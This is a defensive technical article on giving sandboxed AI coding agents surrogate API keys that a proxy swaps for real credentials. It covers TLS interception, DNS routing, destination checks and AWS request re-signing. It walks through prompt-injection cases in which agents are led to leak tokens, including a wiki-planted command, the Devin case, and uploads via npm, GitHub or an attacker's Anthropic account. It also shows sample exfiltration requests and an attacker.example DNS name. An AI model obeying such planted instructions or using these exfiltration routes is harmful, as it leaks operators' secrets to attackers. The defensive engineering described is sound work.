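# Surrogate API credentials for sandboxed AI agents: swapping tokens for real keys at a proxy

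## Why an agent's container is a poor place for an API key

A surrogate API credential is a stand-in for an API key. A program that calls an outside service sends the stand-in with each request, and a proxy replaces it with the real key before the request reaches the service. Vendors also call the stand-in a placeholder, a sentinel, a dummy or a phantom token. Surrogates are used with AI agents that write and run their own commands, usually inside a container, because any of those commands can read a real key stored in the container. Much of the public evidence on how well this approach works comes from the companies that sell it.

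### Keys that work for whoever holds them

An API (application programming interface) is the part of a service that other programs call. An API key is the string by which the service recognises an authorised caller, and most such keys are bearer credentials. Jones and Hardt (2012), in *The OAuth 2.0 Authorization Framework*, define a bearer token by one property: anyone in possession of it can use it in every way that any other holder can, without proving anything further. The caller simply puts the string in a header of the request:

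```
Authorization: Bearer k-51f0c2e97a
```

Unless the service adds restrictions of its own, nothing ties that string to a machine, a network or a person. A copy works as well as the original, and goes on working until the key expires or its owner revokes it. The standard therefore demands encrypted transport. It also advises against putting a token in a web address, since servers are likely to log the address. (Some services ask for a signature over each request instead, in which case the secret itself never travels.)

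A coding agent needs keys like this for ordinary work. The agent is a language model connected to tools, above all a command-line shell, where it runs tests, installs packages and edits files. *Agent Proxy*, documentation from the secrets-management vendor Infisical, lists pushing code, filing tickets and calling external APIs as typical jobs, all of which require some kind of login. *Sandboxing agentic coding tools is a networking problem*, a blog post from Formal, another vendor, adds that almost every installation of Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, has a key to Anthropic's API, and that a developer building a third-party integration needs that party's secrets too.

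Nobody can predict which commands the model will choose, so operators put the shell in a container. *Container security fundamentals part 2* (Datadog Security Labs, 2023) explains that containers are ordinary Linux processes that several kernel mechanisms isolate from the rest of the machine. "Sandbox" is a broader term that also covers small virtual machines and operating-system restrictions on a single program. According to Docker, whose software made containers common, a process in one container cannot see processes in another or on the host, and each container has its own network stack. The kernel also limits a container's use of memory, processor and disk, and the root user, normally unrestricted, has reduced powers inside it. Docker names as a primary risk that the default privileges and shared directories can leave gaps in this isolation, either alone or in combination with a kernel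 vulnerability.

All of these barriers separate the container from everything outside it. Inside, the agent's shell, the packages it installs and the scripts those packages launch share the same files and, commonly, one user account. The barriers therefore don't protect a key in the container from the code they are meant to contain.

### How an environment variable reaches every process

The usual way to hand a program its key is an environment variable, a named string that the operating system gives to the program when it starts. Linux man-pages' *environ(7)* documents the mechanism. For a containerised agent that files tickets, it goes like this:

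1. The operator sets the variable at launch, for example with `docker run -e TICKET_KEY=k-51f0c2e97a agent-image`.
2. The system call that starts a program, `execve`, places the string in the memory of the container's first process.
3. When that process starts another one to run a command, the `fork` call gives the child a copy of its parent's entire environment.
4. The child's own children get copies in turn, unless somebody takes the trouble to remove the variable on the way.

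This gives the ticket key to a test runner, or to the install script of a package the agent just downloaded, though neither needs it.

Reading the value takes one command, `printenv TICKET_KEY`. Linux also exposes the environment of each running process as a file, `/proc/PID/environ`, where PID is the number of the process. According to Linux man-pages' *proc_pid_environ(5)* (2026), access to this file depends on the kernel's check for whether one process may inspect another, which processes under the same user account ordinarily pass. The file holds the environment as it was at launch and does not show later changes. If a program reads its key and then deletes the variable, the key therefore remains in the file, where other processes under the same account can ordinarily read it.

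According to the *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026), Claude Code passes secrets in its environment to the shell commands it runs, whether or not they are sandboxed. It also passes them to hooks, which are commands that run automatically at set points, and to local MCP servers, which are helper programs that give the model extra tools. Many developers keep their secrets in a `.env` file in the project folder, which is no better protected. Formal points out that telling version control to ignore the file keeps it out of the repository but doesn't stop an agent that starts in the same folder from reading it.

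Storing the key in a file instead of an environment variable can still expose it to the agent. Docker recommends mounting each secret as a file that only named services may open, so processes no longer inherit it automatically. But if the agent is the service that needs the secret, its shell can open the file.

### Where the copies go

Complaints about keeping secrets in environment variables predate coding agents. *Why you shouldn't use ENV variables for secret data* (2017) observed that applications often dump their whole environment into error reports. PagerDuty, which handles incident alerts, had received so many secrets that it had a well-practised routine for removing them. Docker also warns that secrets can end up in logs and that it is hard to track who has read a variable.

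An agent adds a new place for a key to leak: the model's context, the text the model works from. Whatever a command prints is added to that text, which is sent to the company hosting the model. *SlotGuard* (2026) assumes a provider that computes honestly but may keep what it receives, including shell output, process listings and file contents. A script that prints its configuration for debugging, including the key, therefore sends the key to a third party with no attacker involved. *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary* (Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues, 2026) lists other places where copies of a key can end up: conversation history, execution logs, the agent's long-term memory, error messages, and generated code, where a key may sit in plain text until someone commits it. Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues work for Corvic AI, which makes a credential vault, but their list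 follows from how agents operate and does not depend on that product. Infisical also lists the shell's command history.

The one sizeable measurement of such leaks covers skills, the packages of instructions and scripts that people download to extend an agent. In *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills*, Chen, Zhang and colleagues (2026) searched the code and descriptions of 17,022 skills, randomly sampled from a large public marketplace, for signs of credential handling. They ran the suspicious ones in a sandbox with mock credentials and sorted the results by hand. They found that 520 skills (3.1%) exposed credentials, 437 because of a vulnerability and 83 because of malice. Debugging output accounted for 1,007 of the 1,371 vulnerability issues, because agent frameworks feed printed text to the model.

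The 3.1% is probably a floor for that marketplace, since the first keyword search excluded 8,343 skills that were never run. It is also weak evidence of how often keys leak from agents in daily use, which would depend on which skills people install and what secrets they leave accessible. The study does establish how keys can leak, and that this mostly needs no attacker. Of the 520 skills, 466 were exploitable in the sandbox, nearly all during routine execution and without special privileges.

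Scanning for leaked keys catches only some leaks. Scanners search stored files, but an agent may leak a key through output that is never stored in a form they read. *Threat Landscape of Vibe Coding and the Road to Secure Autonomy* (2026) identifies this gap in existing defences, and still classes designs in which the agent never holds a long-lived secret as an open research direction.

### Planted instructions and the compromised container

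Besides leaking by accident, a key can be stolen, and the easiest way is often to ask the agent for it. Prompt injection is text planted in material that the agent reads, such as a web page, a code comment or a ticket, to make it follow an attacker's instructions. *Model-Native Computing Architecture* (2026) attributes the problem to the model's inability to tell the user's instructions from instructions embedded in data. Older injection attacks on databases instead exploit a flaw in a program's logic that a programmer can fix. *SkillShield* (2026) notes that a successful injection can do more damage through a coding agent than through a chatbot, because it can delete files or install a backdoor. Kenney and colleagues cite a benchmark by Liu and colleagues in which none of the ten defences tested proved robust.

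ZenML's *Credential proxy*, a tutorial from a machine-learning tools company, describes a hypothetical agent that has to look up a fact in a private wiki. The operator has put the wiki's token in the agent's container as `WIKI_TOKEN`. Somebody has added a line to a wiki page telling the reader to run a command before continuing. The command fetches an address on an outside server, with `$WIKI_TOKEN` at the end of the address. The model takes the line as part of its task and runs the command. The shell replaces the variable's name with its value, so the token ends up in the outside server's access log. No error appears, and the agent carries on. Because the shell made the substitution, the model may never have seen the token, and a filter that searches the model's output for secrets would have found only the variable's name.

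*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) describes how a malicious prompt on an outside site led Devin, a commercial coding agent, to send secrets from its environment to an attacker's server, using the shell and browser it had for legitimate work. The paper proposes stopping the sandbox from contacting arbitrary servers and denying access to secret files by default.

The first of those remedies is a network allowlist, a list of the hosts that the container may contact. It would have stopped the wiki attack as ZenML describes it, but an allowlist can still leave ways to send a key out. Formal examined the firewall in a container template that Anthropic provides for Claude Code and found that it allowed access to the npm package registry and GitHub, along with connections to any address on the port for remote logins. An agent following hostile instructions could publish the key in an npm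 package or post it on GitHub as a snippet, where strangers could read it. Coding agents also have legitimate reasons to use both sites. Formal has an interest in this conclusion because it sells a proxy that inspects traffic in more detail, but anyone can check its reasoning against the list of hosts.

Prompt injection is one of several ways to compromise an agent's container. An attacker can also do it without persuading any model, through a malicious package, as the 83 malicious skills in Chen and colleagues' sample illustrate, or through a flaw in a program the agent runs. The route hardly matters when deciding where to keep a key. It is more useful to assume that the attacker already controls what runs inside the container, can read every file, variable and message the agent can read, and can send whatever the network allows. This assumption does not extend to the host. An attacker who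 breaks out of the container through a kernel vulnerability may reach a proxy running on the host, and the defence then fails.

### Using a credential without reading it

An agent can use a credential without being able to read it, but storing the credential in an environment variable allows both. For the wiki to answer the agent's request, a program only has to add the token before the request arrives. In the surrogate design, the container therefore holds only a surrogate that no outside service accepts, and a proxy outside the container swaps it for the real credential. If the agent prints the surrogate, commits it to a repository or sends it to a stranger, the recipient cannot use it at the service. Tokenizer, from the hosting company Fly.io, is an earlier, similar system.

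Kenney and colleagues trace the reasoning behind such designs to two much older papers. *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975) sets out eight design principles, two of which apply directly to the proxy. Least privilege means that each program should run with "the least set of privileges necessary to complete the job". A test runner that inherits a ticket key plainly violates this principle. Less obviously, so does an agent that can read a key when it only needs the service to accept its requests. Complete mediation requires a check of authority on every access to every object. The operator can't enforce this when a bearer key is in the container, because anyone who copies the key can call the service directly from anywhere. If only the proxy holds the key, it can examine each request that uses it.

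The same paper's concept of a "protected subsystem" is closer to the proxy than either principle is. A protected subsystem is a set of programs with exclusive access to some data, which other programs can reach only by calling the subsystem at fixed entry points. The swapping proxy is a fair example, with the API key as the data.

*The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) describes a compiler at Tymshare, a company that rented out computer time. The compiler had permission to write in its own directory, where it kept usage statistics, and users could name a file to receive its debugging output. One user named the company's billing file, which was in the same directory. The system allowed the write because the compiler had permission, and the billing records were lost. Hardy concluded that the compiler had authority from two sources, its own permission and its user's, and could not specify which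 it was using for a given action. The term "confused deputy" now refers to a program with legitimate authority that is induced to use it by someone who lacks that authority.

The agent in the wiki case fits the description of a deputy, since it holds the operator's token while reading a stranger's instructions. Taking the token out of the container keeps this attacker from stealing it. But the agent is still a deputy, and the proxy arguably becomes a second one, because it now has the authority while the container decides what to request. ZenML acknowledges that in its example any call to an approved host gets the real credential, whatever the call does. If the wiki's token permits deletion, an agent that cannot read the token can still follow a planted instruction to delete a page, and the proxy will authenticate the request.

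## How the proxy exchanges a surrogate for the real key

The proxy can control where the real credential goes, but it can't determine whether the operator would want a given request. Airut, an open-source tool by Pyry Haulos, is a fairly complete example of this design. People send it a task by email or Slack, and it runs Claude Code on the task in a container and replies in the same thread, often with a pull request for someone to review. Haulos's *Developing with Claude Code over Email* explains that the agent works without asking for approval at each step, so the infrastructure around it has to limit the damage. The containers run under Podman, an alternative to Docker, in "rootless" mode, so an ordinary user account on the host owns them.

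The current version of Airut is 0.28.0, from November 2026. Developers can also use its sandbox on its own as a Python library. The design descriptions below come from Airut's developer, but others can check them against the code, which is public under the MIT licence.

### Setting up the surrogate

Before the container starts, the operator gives the real credential to software on the host and lists the hosts that may receive it. Airut keeps its credentials in the server's configuration, which the operator edits as a file or through a web dashboard. Docker's sandbox product has a command that shows what such a registration contains. Docker's *Manage credentials* calls the feature "custom secrets" and labels it experimental. For the ticket-filing agent of the previous section, the command would be:

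```
sbx secret set-custom --host api.tickets.example \
    --env TICKET_KEY --value "$REAL_KEY"
```

The first option sets the host scope, the second names the environment variable that the container will see, and the third supplies the real credential. Docker warns against typing the key itself into the command because the shell would save it in its history.

The software then generates a surrogate, which should be random. If it were the real key with a few characters changed, a leaked surrogate would reveal most of the key. The surrogate must also be long enough never to appear in ordinary traffic by chance, since the proxy recognises it only by its text.

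Airut's surrogates are format-preserving, so they look like the credentials they replace. If the real key is `k-` followed by ten hexadecimal digits, the surrogate is `k-` followed by ten other hexadecimal digits. This matters because some programs check a key before they use it. In *How I Sandbox AI Coding Agents*, zachoverzero found that Claude Code checks its login token locally, before it contacts any server, and stops if the value doesn't look like a real token. GitHub's command-line tool is less strict: it won't run without a token in `GH_TOKEN`, but it accepts the word "placeholder", according to *Proxy Mode*, the documentation of another sandboxing tool, devsandbox. An HTTP request also declares the length of its body, so keeping the surrogate the same length as the key means the proxy doesn't have to correct that number when it makes a replacement there.

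*LLMs Behind Bars*, a set of 2026 conference slides, describes a variant in which the surrogate is an encrypted token containing the rules for its use. The proxy can decrypt the token, so it doesn't have to store a record for each surrogate. However, this makes the key's format harder to preserve, and the slides list failed format validation as a drawback.

Finally, the container starts with `TICKET_KEY` set to the surrogate, so a program that reads the variable does not get the real key. This protection applies only to keys that the operator has registered for masking. The short code example on Airut's package page passes a variable named `key` into the container's environment as `ANTHROPIC_API_KEY` without requesting a surrogate. The swap also does not help if a `.env` file in the repository contains a second copy of the real key.

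### One request, from start to finish

Suppose the real credential is `k-51f0c2e97a`, the surrogate is `k-9b3e70d4c6`, and the host scope contains only `api.tickets.example`. The network allowlist contains that host and `packages.example`, a package registry. All of these values are invented. When the agent files a ticket, the exchange goes as follows:

1. The agent runs a script that uses the ticket service's SDK (software development kit), a ready-made client library. The SDK reads `TICKET_KEY` and puts the value into an `Authorization` header. It needs no modification, because it handles the surrogate like any other key.
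2. The SDK opens an encrypted connection to `api.tickets.example`. The container's network leads to the proxy, which answers in the service's place and decrypts the request.
3. The proxy looks for the host on the network allowlist. If the host is missing, the proxy refuses the request.
4. The proxy opens its own encrypted connection to `api.tickets.example` and checks the service's certificate.
5. Because this host is in the surrogate's host scope, the proxy replaces the surrogate with the real credential.
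6. The proxy forwards the request and passes the service's response back to the container.

The container sends this:

```
POST /v1/tickets HTTP/1.1
Host: api.tickets.example
Authorization: Bearer k-9b3e70d4c6
Content-Type: application/json
Content-Length: 29

{"title":"Login page broken"}
```

The ticket service receives this:

```
POST /v1/tickets HTTP/1.1
Host: api.tickets.example
Authorization: Bearer k-51f0c2e97a
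Content-Type: application/json
Content-Length: 29

{"title":"Login page broken"}
```

Now suppose that the agent reads a planted instruction to publish its key on the package registry. It sends:

```
POST /v1/packages HTTP/1.1
Host: packages.example
Content-Type: text/plain
Content-Length: 23

TICKET_KEY=k-9b3e70d4c6
```

The registry is on the allowlist, so the proxy forwards the request. It does so without changing the body, because the registry is outside the surrogate's host scope. The attacker downloads the package and tries `k-9b3e70d4c6` at the ticket service from another machine, but gets an error because the service never issued that key.

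| Where the value appears | Request to `api.tickets.example` | Request to `packages.example` |
|---|---|---|
| Container's memory, files and logs | `k-9b3e70d4c6` | `k-9b3e70d4c6` |
| Network between container and proxy | encrypted | encrypted |
| Proxy, on arrival | `k-9b3e70d4c6` | `k-9b3e70d4c6` |
| Proxy, on departure | `k-51f0c2e97a` | `k-9b3e70d4c6` |
| Network between proxy and host | encrypted | encrypted |
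| Receiving host | `k-51f0c2e97a` | `k-9b3e70d4c6` |

The real credential appears only in the proxy and at the ticket service, unless the service repeats it in a response (reflection), which would also send it to the container.

### The swap rule

Let *s* be a surrogate, *k* its real credential and *H* its host scope. Let *x* be the content of a request and *d* its verified destination, the host that the proxy has confirmed will receive it. The proxy then forwards:

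```
swap(x, d) = x with s replaced by k,   if d ∈ H
swap(x, d) = x unchanged,              if d ∉ H
```

A container with several credentials has one such triple for each, and the proxy applies the rule to each triple separately. If the container also has a surrogate for a GitHub token and sends the ticket surrogate to GitHub, GitHub receives the surrogate rather than the real key, because GitHub's hosts are not in the ticket key's scope. Deno's *Security*, the documentation for a hosted sandbox, likewise says that the secret replaces its surrogate only in requests to an approved host.

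Systems differ in how much of the request they search for the surrogate. Docker's custom secrets replace it anywhere in the request, including the body. A plain text search misses a surrogate that the client has compressed, encoded or used to compute a signature. With header injection, the proxy writes the authentication header itself, so it doesn't need to search for a surrogate.

The rule's destination check deserves more scrutiny than its text replacement because its errors can be more serious. If the proxy fails to replace a surrogate bound for an approved host, the service rejects the request and someone has to fix the configuration. If the proxy wrongly treats *d* as a member of *H*, it sends the real credential to an unapproved host.

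The operator can change *k* without changing *s* because the container never depends on *k*. Blaxel, a sandbox provider whose proxy was still in public preview, lets operators rotate secrets while a sandbox is running. Docker allows this for secrets that belong to a single sandbox, but the operator has to recreate the sandbox after changing a global secret.

### Reading encrypted requests

The proxy has to read a request to find the surrogate in it, but nearly all API traffic is encrypted with TLS (Transport Layer Security), the protocol behind `https` addresses. When a client connects, the service presents a certificate that ties its host name to a public key. The client accepts the certificate if a certificate authority (CA) that the client trusts has signed it. The client and service then agree on encryption keys that nobody between them has, so a proxy that only relays the connection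 can read the host name but not the `Authorization` header.

TLS interception replaces this one connection with two. The proxy generates its own CA, and the operator or the sandbox's setup script adds that CA to the container's trusted list. When the SDK connects to `api.tickets.example`, the proxy creates a certificate for that name, signs it with its CA and presents it. The SDK accepts the certificate because a trusted CA signed it, then sends its request, which the proxy can decrypt. The proxy edits the request and forwards it to the real service over a second TLS connection.

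McCanna points out in *Inspecting Claude Code’s Network Traffic with Linux Namespaces and MITM Proxying* that only the client's trust settings need to change, so the service stays as it is. "MITM" stands for "man in the middle", the usual name for this technique when an attacker uses it. McCanna notes that the proxy uses the same mechanism as an attacker and that the difference is who has authorised it.

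Making every program in the container trust the new CA can take some work, because programs look for their trusted authorities in different places. devsandbox sets five environment variables for the purpose:

| Variable | Programs that read it |
|---|---|
| `NODE_EXTRA_CA_CERTS` | Node.js |
| `REQUESTS_CA_BUNDLE` | Python's `requests` library |
| `CURL_CA_BUNDLE` | curl |
| `GIT_SSL_CAINFO` | Git over HTTPS |
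| `SSL_CERT_FILE` | other programs that use TLS |

A program that does not trust the CA rejects the proxy's certificate, and its request fails. Programs that use certificate pinning reject it whatever the settings, because they accept only a certificate or key that their developers chose in advance. Some cloud SDKs use pinning, according to devsandbox. The operator can switch off interception to accommodate these programs, but the proxy then logs only host names for HTTPS traffic and can't add credentials to it.

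Interception also creates a new secret, the CA's private key. Anyone who has it can impersonate any website to any program that trusts the CA, so the key has to stay with the proxy. The CA's certificate can safely sit in the container. Limiting which programs trust the CA is also prudent. McCanna limits that trust to a single process instead of installing the CA for the whole machine.

### Getting the traffic to the proxy

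Many sandboxes direct requests to the proxy with environment variables. The setup script puts the proxy's address in `HTTP_PROXY` and `HTTPS_PROXY`, which many HTTP clients read by convention. For an `https` address, the client first sends the proxy a line in plain text and then starts TLS over the same connection:

```
CONNECT api.tickets.example:443 HTTP/1.1
```

Grepular's *Auth Proxy Injection for LLMs* describes one such setup, where mitmproxy, a widely used interception program, runs in a second container beside the agent's.

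This is easy to set up, but some clients ignore the variables, and code in the container can remove them with one command. Grepular argues that this is not a flaw, because a request that bypasses the proxy lacks the authentication header and so gets no access to the API. That is correct for the credential, but other data in the container can leave by the same direct route unless something blocks it.

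Several systems block connections that bypass the proxy. Pluto Security's *Inside Claude Managed Agents* reports that unsetting the proxy variables in Anthropic's hosted agent service does not give the container another way to reach the internet. The container has no direct access to DNS, which turns host names into network addresses, and a firewall blocks its direct outbound connections. NanoClaw, which runs agents in containers, has an optional lockdown setting that puts them on an internal Docker network with no route to the internet, so the proxy is the only machine they can reach. Containers have ordinary internet access until the operator turns this setting on.

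Airut's proxy is transparent, which means that clients need no proxy settings at all. Its package page describes a "DNS-spoofing proxy" that requires neither proxy variables nor `iptables` rules (`iptables` is a Linux firewall tool). In a design of this type, a request reaches the proxy in three steps:

1. The SDK asks for the network address of `api.tickets.example`.
2. The DNS server assigned to the container replies with the proxy's own address.
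3. The SDK connects to that address and begins TLS. Its first message normally contains the requested host name in readable form, in a field called SNI (server name indication). The proxy uses this name to create the matching certificate.

Any client that looks up host names in the normal way reaches the proxy, even if it ignores `HTTP_PROXY`, but it must still trust the proxy's CA. Controlling DNS also closes another leak. A program can hide data in the name it looks up, such as `c291cmNl.attacker.example`, and an ordinary DNS server would forward that query to a server the attacker runs. A DNS server that itself answers with the proxy's address doesn't need to forward the query. Airut's website, *Sandboxed Claude Code over email and Slack*, credits its custom DNS with preventing exfiltration, the unauthorised removal of data.

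DNS alone cannot force all traffic through the proxy, because a program that connects directly to an IP address makes no DNS lookup. The website's claim that all traffic passes through the proxy therefore also depends on a container network with no other exit, like the one NanoClaw documents.

Docker's sandboxes use both approaches. Agents use a conventional forward proxy for HTTP and HTTPS, while the system forwards other traffic transparently. According to Docker, the rules on permitted destinations apply to both paths, and the forward proxy injects credentials.

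### Checking the destination

An attacker who controls the container controls everything the container sends the proxy about a request's destination, including the `CONNECT` line, the SNI field, the `Host` header and, with some kinds of routing, the numeric address. Suppose the attacker has a server at 203.0.113.9. Code in the container opens a connection to that address but gives `api.tickets.example` as the host name throughout. A proxy that checked only the host name would find it in the host scope, insert the real credential and forward the request to the attacker's server, giving the attacker the key.

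To prevent this, the proxy should take only the name from the container and look up the address itself, using a DNS server the container cannot influence. The lookup could still return a wrong address, for instance if someone has tampered with DNS upstream. So before it sends the credential, the proxy must also check that the server's certificate is valid for the name and comes from an authority the proxy trusts. An impostor can copy the ticket service's certificate but can't complete the TLS handshake without the matching private key.

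Only the proxy can verify the ticket service's certificate. The SDK would normally do this itself, but when the proxy intercepts the connection, the SDK sees only the certificate that the proxy made. If the proxy skips verification, perhaps because a developer turned it off to get past an error, the SDK will report a secure connection even if the proxy has connected to an impostor.

A client can also put an approved host in the SNI field and a different one in the `Host` header, a technique called domain fronting. Large content delivery networks serve many customers from the same machines and often use the header to choose which customer's site to serve, so the request may reach a different customer from the one the proxy approved. A proxy can prevent this by rejecting requests in which the two names differ.

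Code can get out of a sandbox if the policy engine and the proxy interpret the same host name differently, according to Vercel's *A sandbox without a network boundary is only half a sandbox*. A simpler error is matching names too loosely. A test for names that end in `tickets.example` would also accept `evil-tickets.example`, which anyone could register. Docker avoids this by matching the parts between the dots. In its host lists, `*.example.com` covers one additional part and `**.example.com` covers any number. Such patterns are convenient, but they extend the host scope to every matching host, including any that outsiders can publish on.

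Looking up the name also lets the proxy inspect the resulting address. Docker's documentation from March 2026 describes a default policy that blocks addresses belonging to private networks and to the host machine. Because the proxy checks the address as well as the name, a container cannot reach the host by calling it `ip6-localhost` instead of `localhost`.

Plain HTTP has no certificate, so the proxy cannot verify *d* and should leave the surrogate in place. Swapping in the real key would also send it across the network in readable form. The container chooses between `http` and `https`, so if the proxy made the swap, an attacker able to listen to traffic beyond it could have the agent request `http://api.tickets.example` and copy the key as it passed.

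According to its *Internet access* documentation, E2B, another sandbox provider, therefore injects headers only into intercepted TLS traffic. Sandbox0's *Network Policy* lists plain HTTP as supported too. An operator might want that for an old service on a private network, but anyone who can read traffic on that network can then read the credential.

If the ticket service redirects the client to another host, the SDK sends a new request. Any credential in that request is still the surrogate, and the proxy applies the swap rule to the new destination. If the proxy followed the redirect itself and kept the real credential in the header, it would send that credential to the new host.

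### Host scope and network allowlist

The network allowlist and the host scope are easy to confuse because both are lists of hosts. A request can leave only if its destination is on the allowlist, and it carries the real credential only if that destination is also in the host scope.

| | Host in the surrogate's scope | Host outside the scope |
|---|---|---|
| **On the allowlist** | Proxy forwards the request with the real credential | Proxy forwards the request with the surrogate |
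| **Not on the allowlist** | Proxy refuses the request | Proxy refuses the request |

E2B sets header rules and network access separately, so a header rule for a host does not by itself allow the sandbox to contact that host.

The host scope protects the credential, while the allowlist protects everything else the container can read, such as source code, customer records and the agent's conversation. Vercel observes that a generated program with unrestricted network access can send whatever it can read to an outside server without breaking out of its sandbox.

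A surrogate protects the real key but not the container's other data. Docker's default policy of March 2026 permitted all traffic except to blocked address ranges. Under that policy, a compromised container could have sent the whole repository to an attacker's server, but not a proxy-managed key, because it had only the surrogate. A program that bypasses the proxy also has no usable credential, but nothing restricts where it sends other data.

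Even with an allowlist, data can leave through an approved host, as in Formal's npm and GitHub examples. Haulos's *Why You (Probably) Should Not Give Your Agent GitHub Access* gives another example, which affects every installation of Claude Code. Claude Code cannot work without `api.anthropic.com`, so the allowlist has to include that host. But an attacker can supply a key to their own Anthropic account and have the agent upload files to that account. The swap rule has no effect because the request contains no surrogate.

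Airut's remedy is to drop credentials that do not match the expected token, a technique Haulos calls foreign credential detection. Surrogates make this fairly straightforward because the proxy has a record of the value a legitimate request should contain and can treat any other value in that header as suspect. Airut's allowlist can also restrict a request's path and method, for instance to limit GitHub operations to particular repositories.

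Haulos nevertheless concludes from his experience with GitHub that path rules and surrogates together are not enough, and that the proxy has to inspect requests more deeply. He also acknowledges that every addition to the policy code makes an exploitable bug more likely. Haulos is judging his own product, but his conclusion carries some weight because it runs against his commercial or personal interest in presenting the simpler version as adequate.

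### Keeping the policy out of the agent's reach

The security of the swap rule depends on the list *H*. If an attacker can add `attacker.example` to it, the proxy will send the real key to that host. Adding a host to the allowlist likewise allows other data to be sent there. Both lists must therefore be stored where the agent cannot change them.

A coding agent edits files in a repository, and Airut keeps each project's allowlist and container settings in the `.airut/` directory of that same repository, where developers can review them like any other code. The agent can edit its working copy of this directory, but those edits have no effect because Airut reads the settings from the repository's default branch. The agent can propose a new host in a pull request, but the change applies only after the request is merged.

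This protection fails if the agent's own GitHub token lets it write to the default branch or merge its own pull requests, because the agent can then approve its own changes to the allowlist. The operator has to prevent this with branch protection, a GitHub setting that can require another person's approval. The reviewer also has to notice one added line in `.airut/` among what may be hundreds of changed lines elsewhere.

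Docker instead keeps approvals in a file on the host, outside the sandbox. When a user first runs a third-party extension that needs a credential, Docker prompts the user for the domains that may receive it and records the answer. It prompts again if the extension later requests a domain that the record does not cover. If nobody is there to answer, as in an automated run, the sandbox starts without the credential.

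Control panels need the same protection as files. Airut's dashboard, where the operator configures credentials, is available at port 5200 on the host. A container that could reach that port and log in could change the settings that are supposed to confine it. Blocking connections to the host's own addresses, as Docker's default policy does, prevents this.

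## Signed requests, OAuth logins and Git

The swap rule works only if the surrogate appears in the request as text, and some protocols hide it. In HTTP Basic authentication, the client joins a user name and a password with a colon and encodes the result in base64, a way of writing any data in 64 ordinary characters. For the user name `bot` and the ticket surrogate `k-9b3e70d4c6`, the header is:

```
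Authorization: Basic Ym90OmstOWIzZTcwZDRjNg==
```

A text search can't find the surrogate in a base64-encoded header. OpenShell, NVIDIA's sandbox for AI agents, decodes the header, replaces the surrogate and encodes the result again, according to NVIDIA's *Providers*. Services that require a cryptographic signature need a different mechanism, because a signature can't be reversed.

### Why a surrogate cannot sign an AWS request

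Amazon Web Services (AWS) authenticates requests with Signature Version 4 (SigV4). The customer has an access key ID, which is not secret, and a secret access key. The client uses the secret key to compute a signature over each request, then sends the ID and the signature but never the secret key. AWS repeats the calculation and compares the results.

AWS's *Signature Calculations for the Authorization Header* gives a worked example that programmers can use to test their code. It reads the first ten bytes of `test.txt` from a bucket in S3, Amazon's file storage, with a published dummy key:

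```
Access key ID:      AKIAIOSFODNN7EXAMPLE
Secret access key:  wJalrXUtnFEMI/K7MDENG/bPxRfiCYEXAMPLEKEY
```

The client first writes the request in a standard form, the canonical request, which here has ten lines:

| Line | Text | What it holds |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | `GET` | The method |
| 2 | `/test.txt` | The path |
| 3 | (empty) | Query parameters, of which this request has none |
| 4 | `host:examplebucket.s3.amazonaws.com` | First header: the bucket's address |
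| 5 | `range:bytes=0-9` | Second header: which bytes the client wants |
| 6 | `x-amz-content-sha256:e3b0c44298fc1c149afbf4c8996fb92427ae41e4649b934ca495991b7852b855` | Third header: the SHA-256 hash of the body |
| 7 | `x-amz-date:20130524T000000Z` | Fourth header: the time of the request |
| 8 | (empty) | End of the headers |
| 9 | `host;range;x-amz-content-sha256;x-amz-date` | Names of the headers that the signature covers |
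| 10 | The same 64 digits as in line 6 | The hash of the body again |

SHA-256 reduces any data to 64 hexadecimal digits, and these are the digits for an empty body.

The client then hashes the whole canonical request and puts the result on the last line of the string to sign:

```
AWS4-HMAC-SHA256
20130524T000000Z
20130524/us-east-1/s3/aws4_request
7344ae5b7ee6c3e7e6b0fe0640412a37625d1fbfff95c48bbb2dc43964946972
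```

The third line restricts the signature to one date, one AWS region and one service. The secret comes in only now. HMAC-SHA256 is a keyed hash, a function that combines a key and a message into a value that nobody can compute without the key. The client applies it four times to derive a signing key, and once more to sign:

```
k1        = HMAC("AWS4" + secret, "20130524")
k2        = HMAC(k1, "us-east-1")
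k3        = HMAC(k2, "s3")
key       = HMAC(k3, "aws4_request")
signature = HMAC(key, string to sign)
          = f0e8bdb87c964420e857bd35b5d6ed310bd44f0170aba48dd91039c6036bdb41
```

A client that holds a surrogate secret produces the same canonical request and string to sign, but its `k1` is different, and so is every value derived from it, including the signature. AWS computes the signature above from the real secret and rejects the request because the two don't match. The proxy can replace a surrogate access key ID with the real one, but it also has to discard the client's signature and compute a new one from the real secret.

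NVIDIA's *AWS SigV4 Credential Signing* describes how OpenShell does this. The operator gives the real key pair to OpenShell, and inside the sandbox sets both AWS variables to the word `placeholder`. The AWS SDK signs with these values as usual and puts the result in the `Authorization` header. The proxy removes that header, signs the request with the real secret and writes a new one. If the proxy keeps the time and the list of signed headers from the example request, the two headers differ in only two places:

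| Part of the header | Sent by the container | Sent by the proxy |
|---|---|---|
| Access key ID | `placeholder` | `AKIAIOSFODNN7EXAMPLE` |
| Signature | 64 digits that AWS would reject | `f0e8bdb8…036bdb41`, the value computed above |

Fly.io's Tokenizer can also sign requests, as can the sandbox proxy of LangSmith, a platform for building agents, according to LangChain's *aws_auth*.

An operator could instead give the container the derived signing key and keep the secret elsewhere. AWS suggests this for companies with many servers, since the derived key works for only one region and service and lasts at most seven days. But it is still a real credential, so anyone who copied it from an agent's container could sign S3 requests from another machine for up to a week.

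### What the signing proxy has to know

The proxy needs the service and the region to derive the key. OpenShell takes the service from the operator's policy and the region from the host name, and the operator can set the region by hand for unusual addresses. Varlock, another credential proxy, reads both values from the surrogate's signature, so it blocks any AWS request that arrives unsigned, according to its *AWS SigV4 Plugin* documentation.

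Varlock's approach needs less configuration, because one rule for `*.amazonaws.com` covers every AWS service. But it lets the container choose the service. The operator can restrict the choice with a list such as `allowedServices=[bedrock, s3]`. Without that list, the proxy signs requests to any AWS service, and only the real key's permissions limit what the container can do.

Temporary AWS keys come with a third value, a session token, which goes in its own header. Some services require the signature to cover that header, so for those the proxy must add the token before signing. OpenShell's gateway, the component that stores credentials outside the sandbox, can request temporary keys from AWS and renew them itself.

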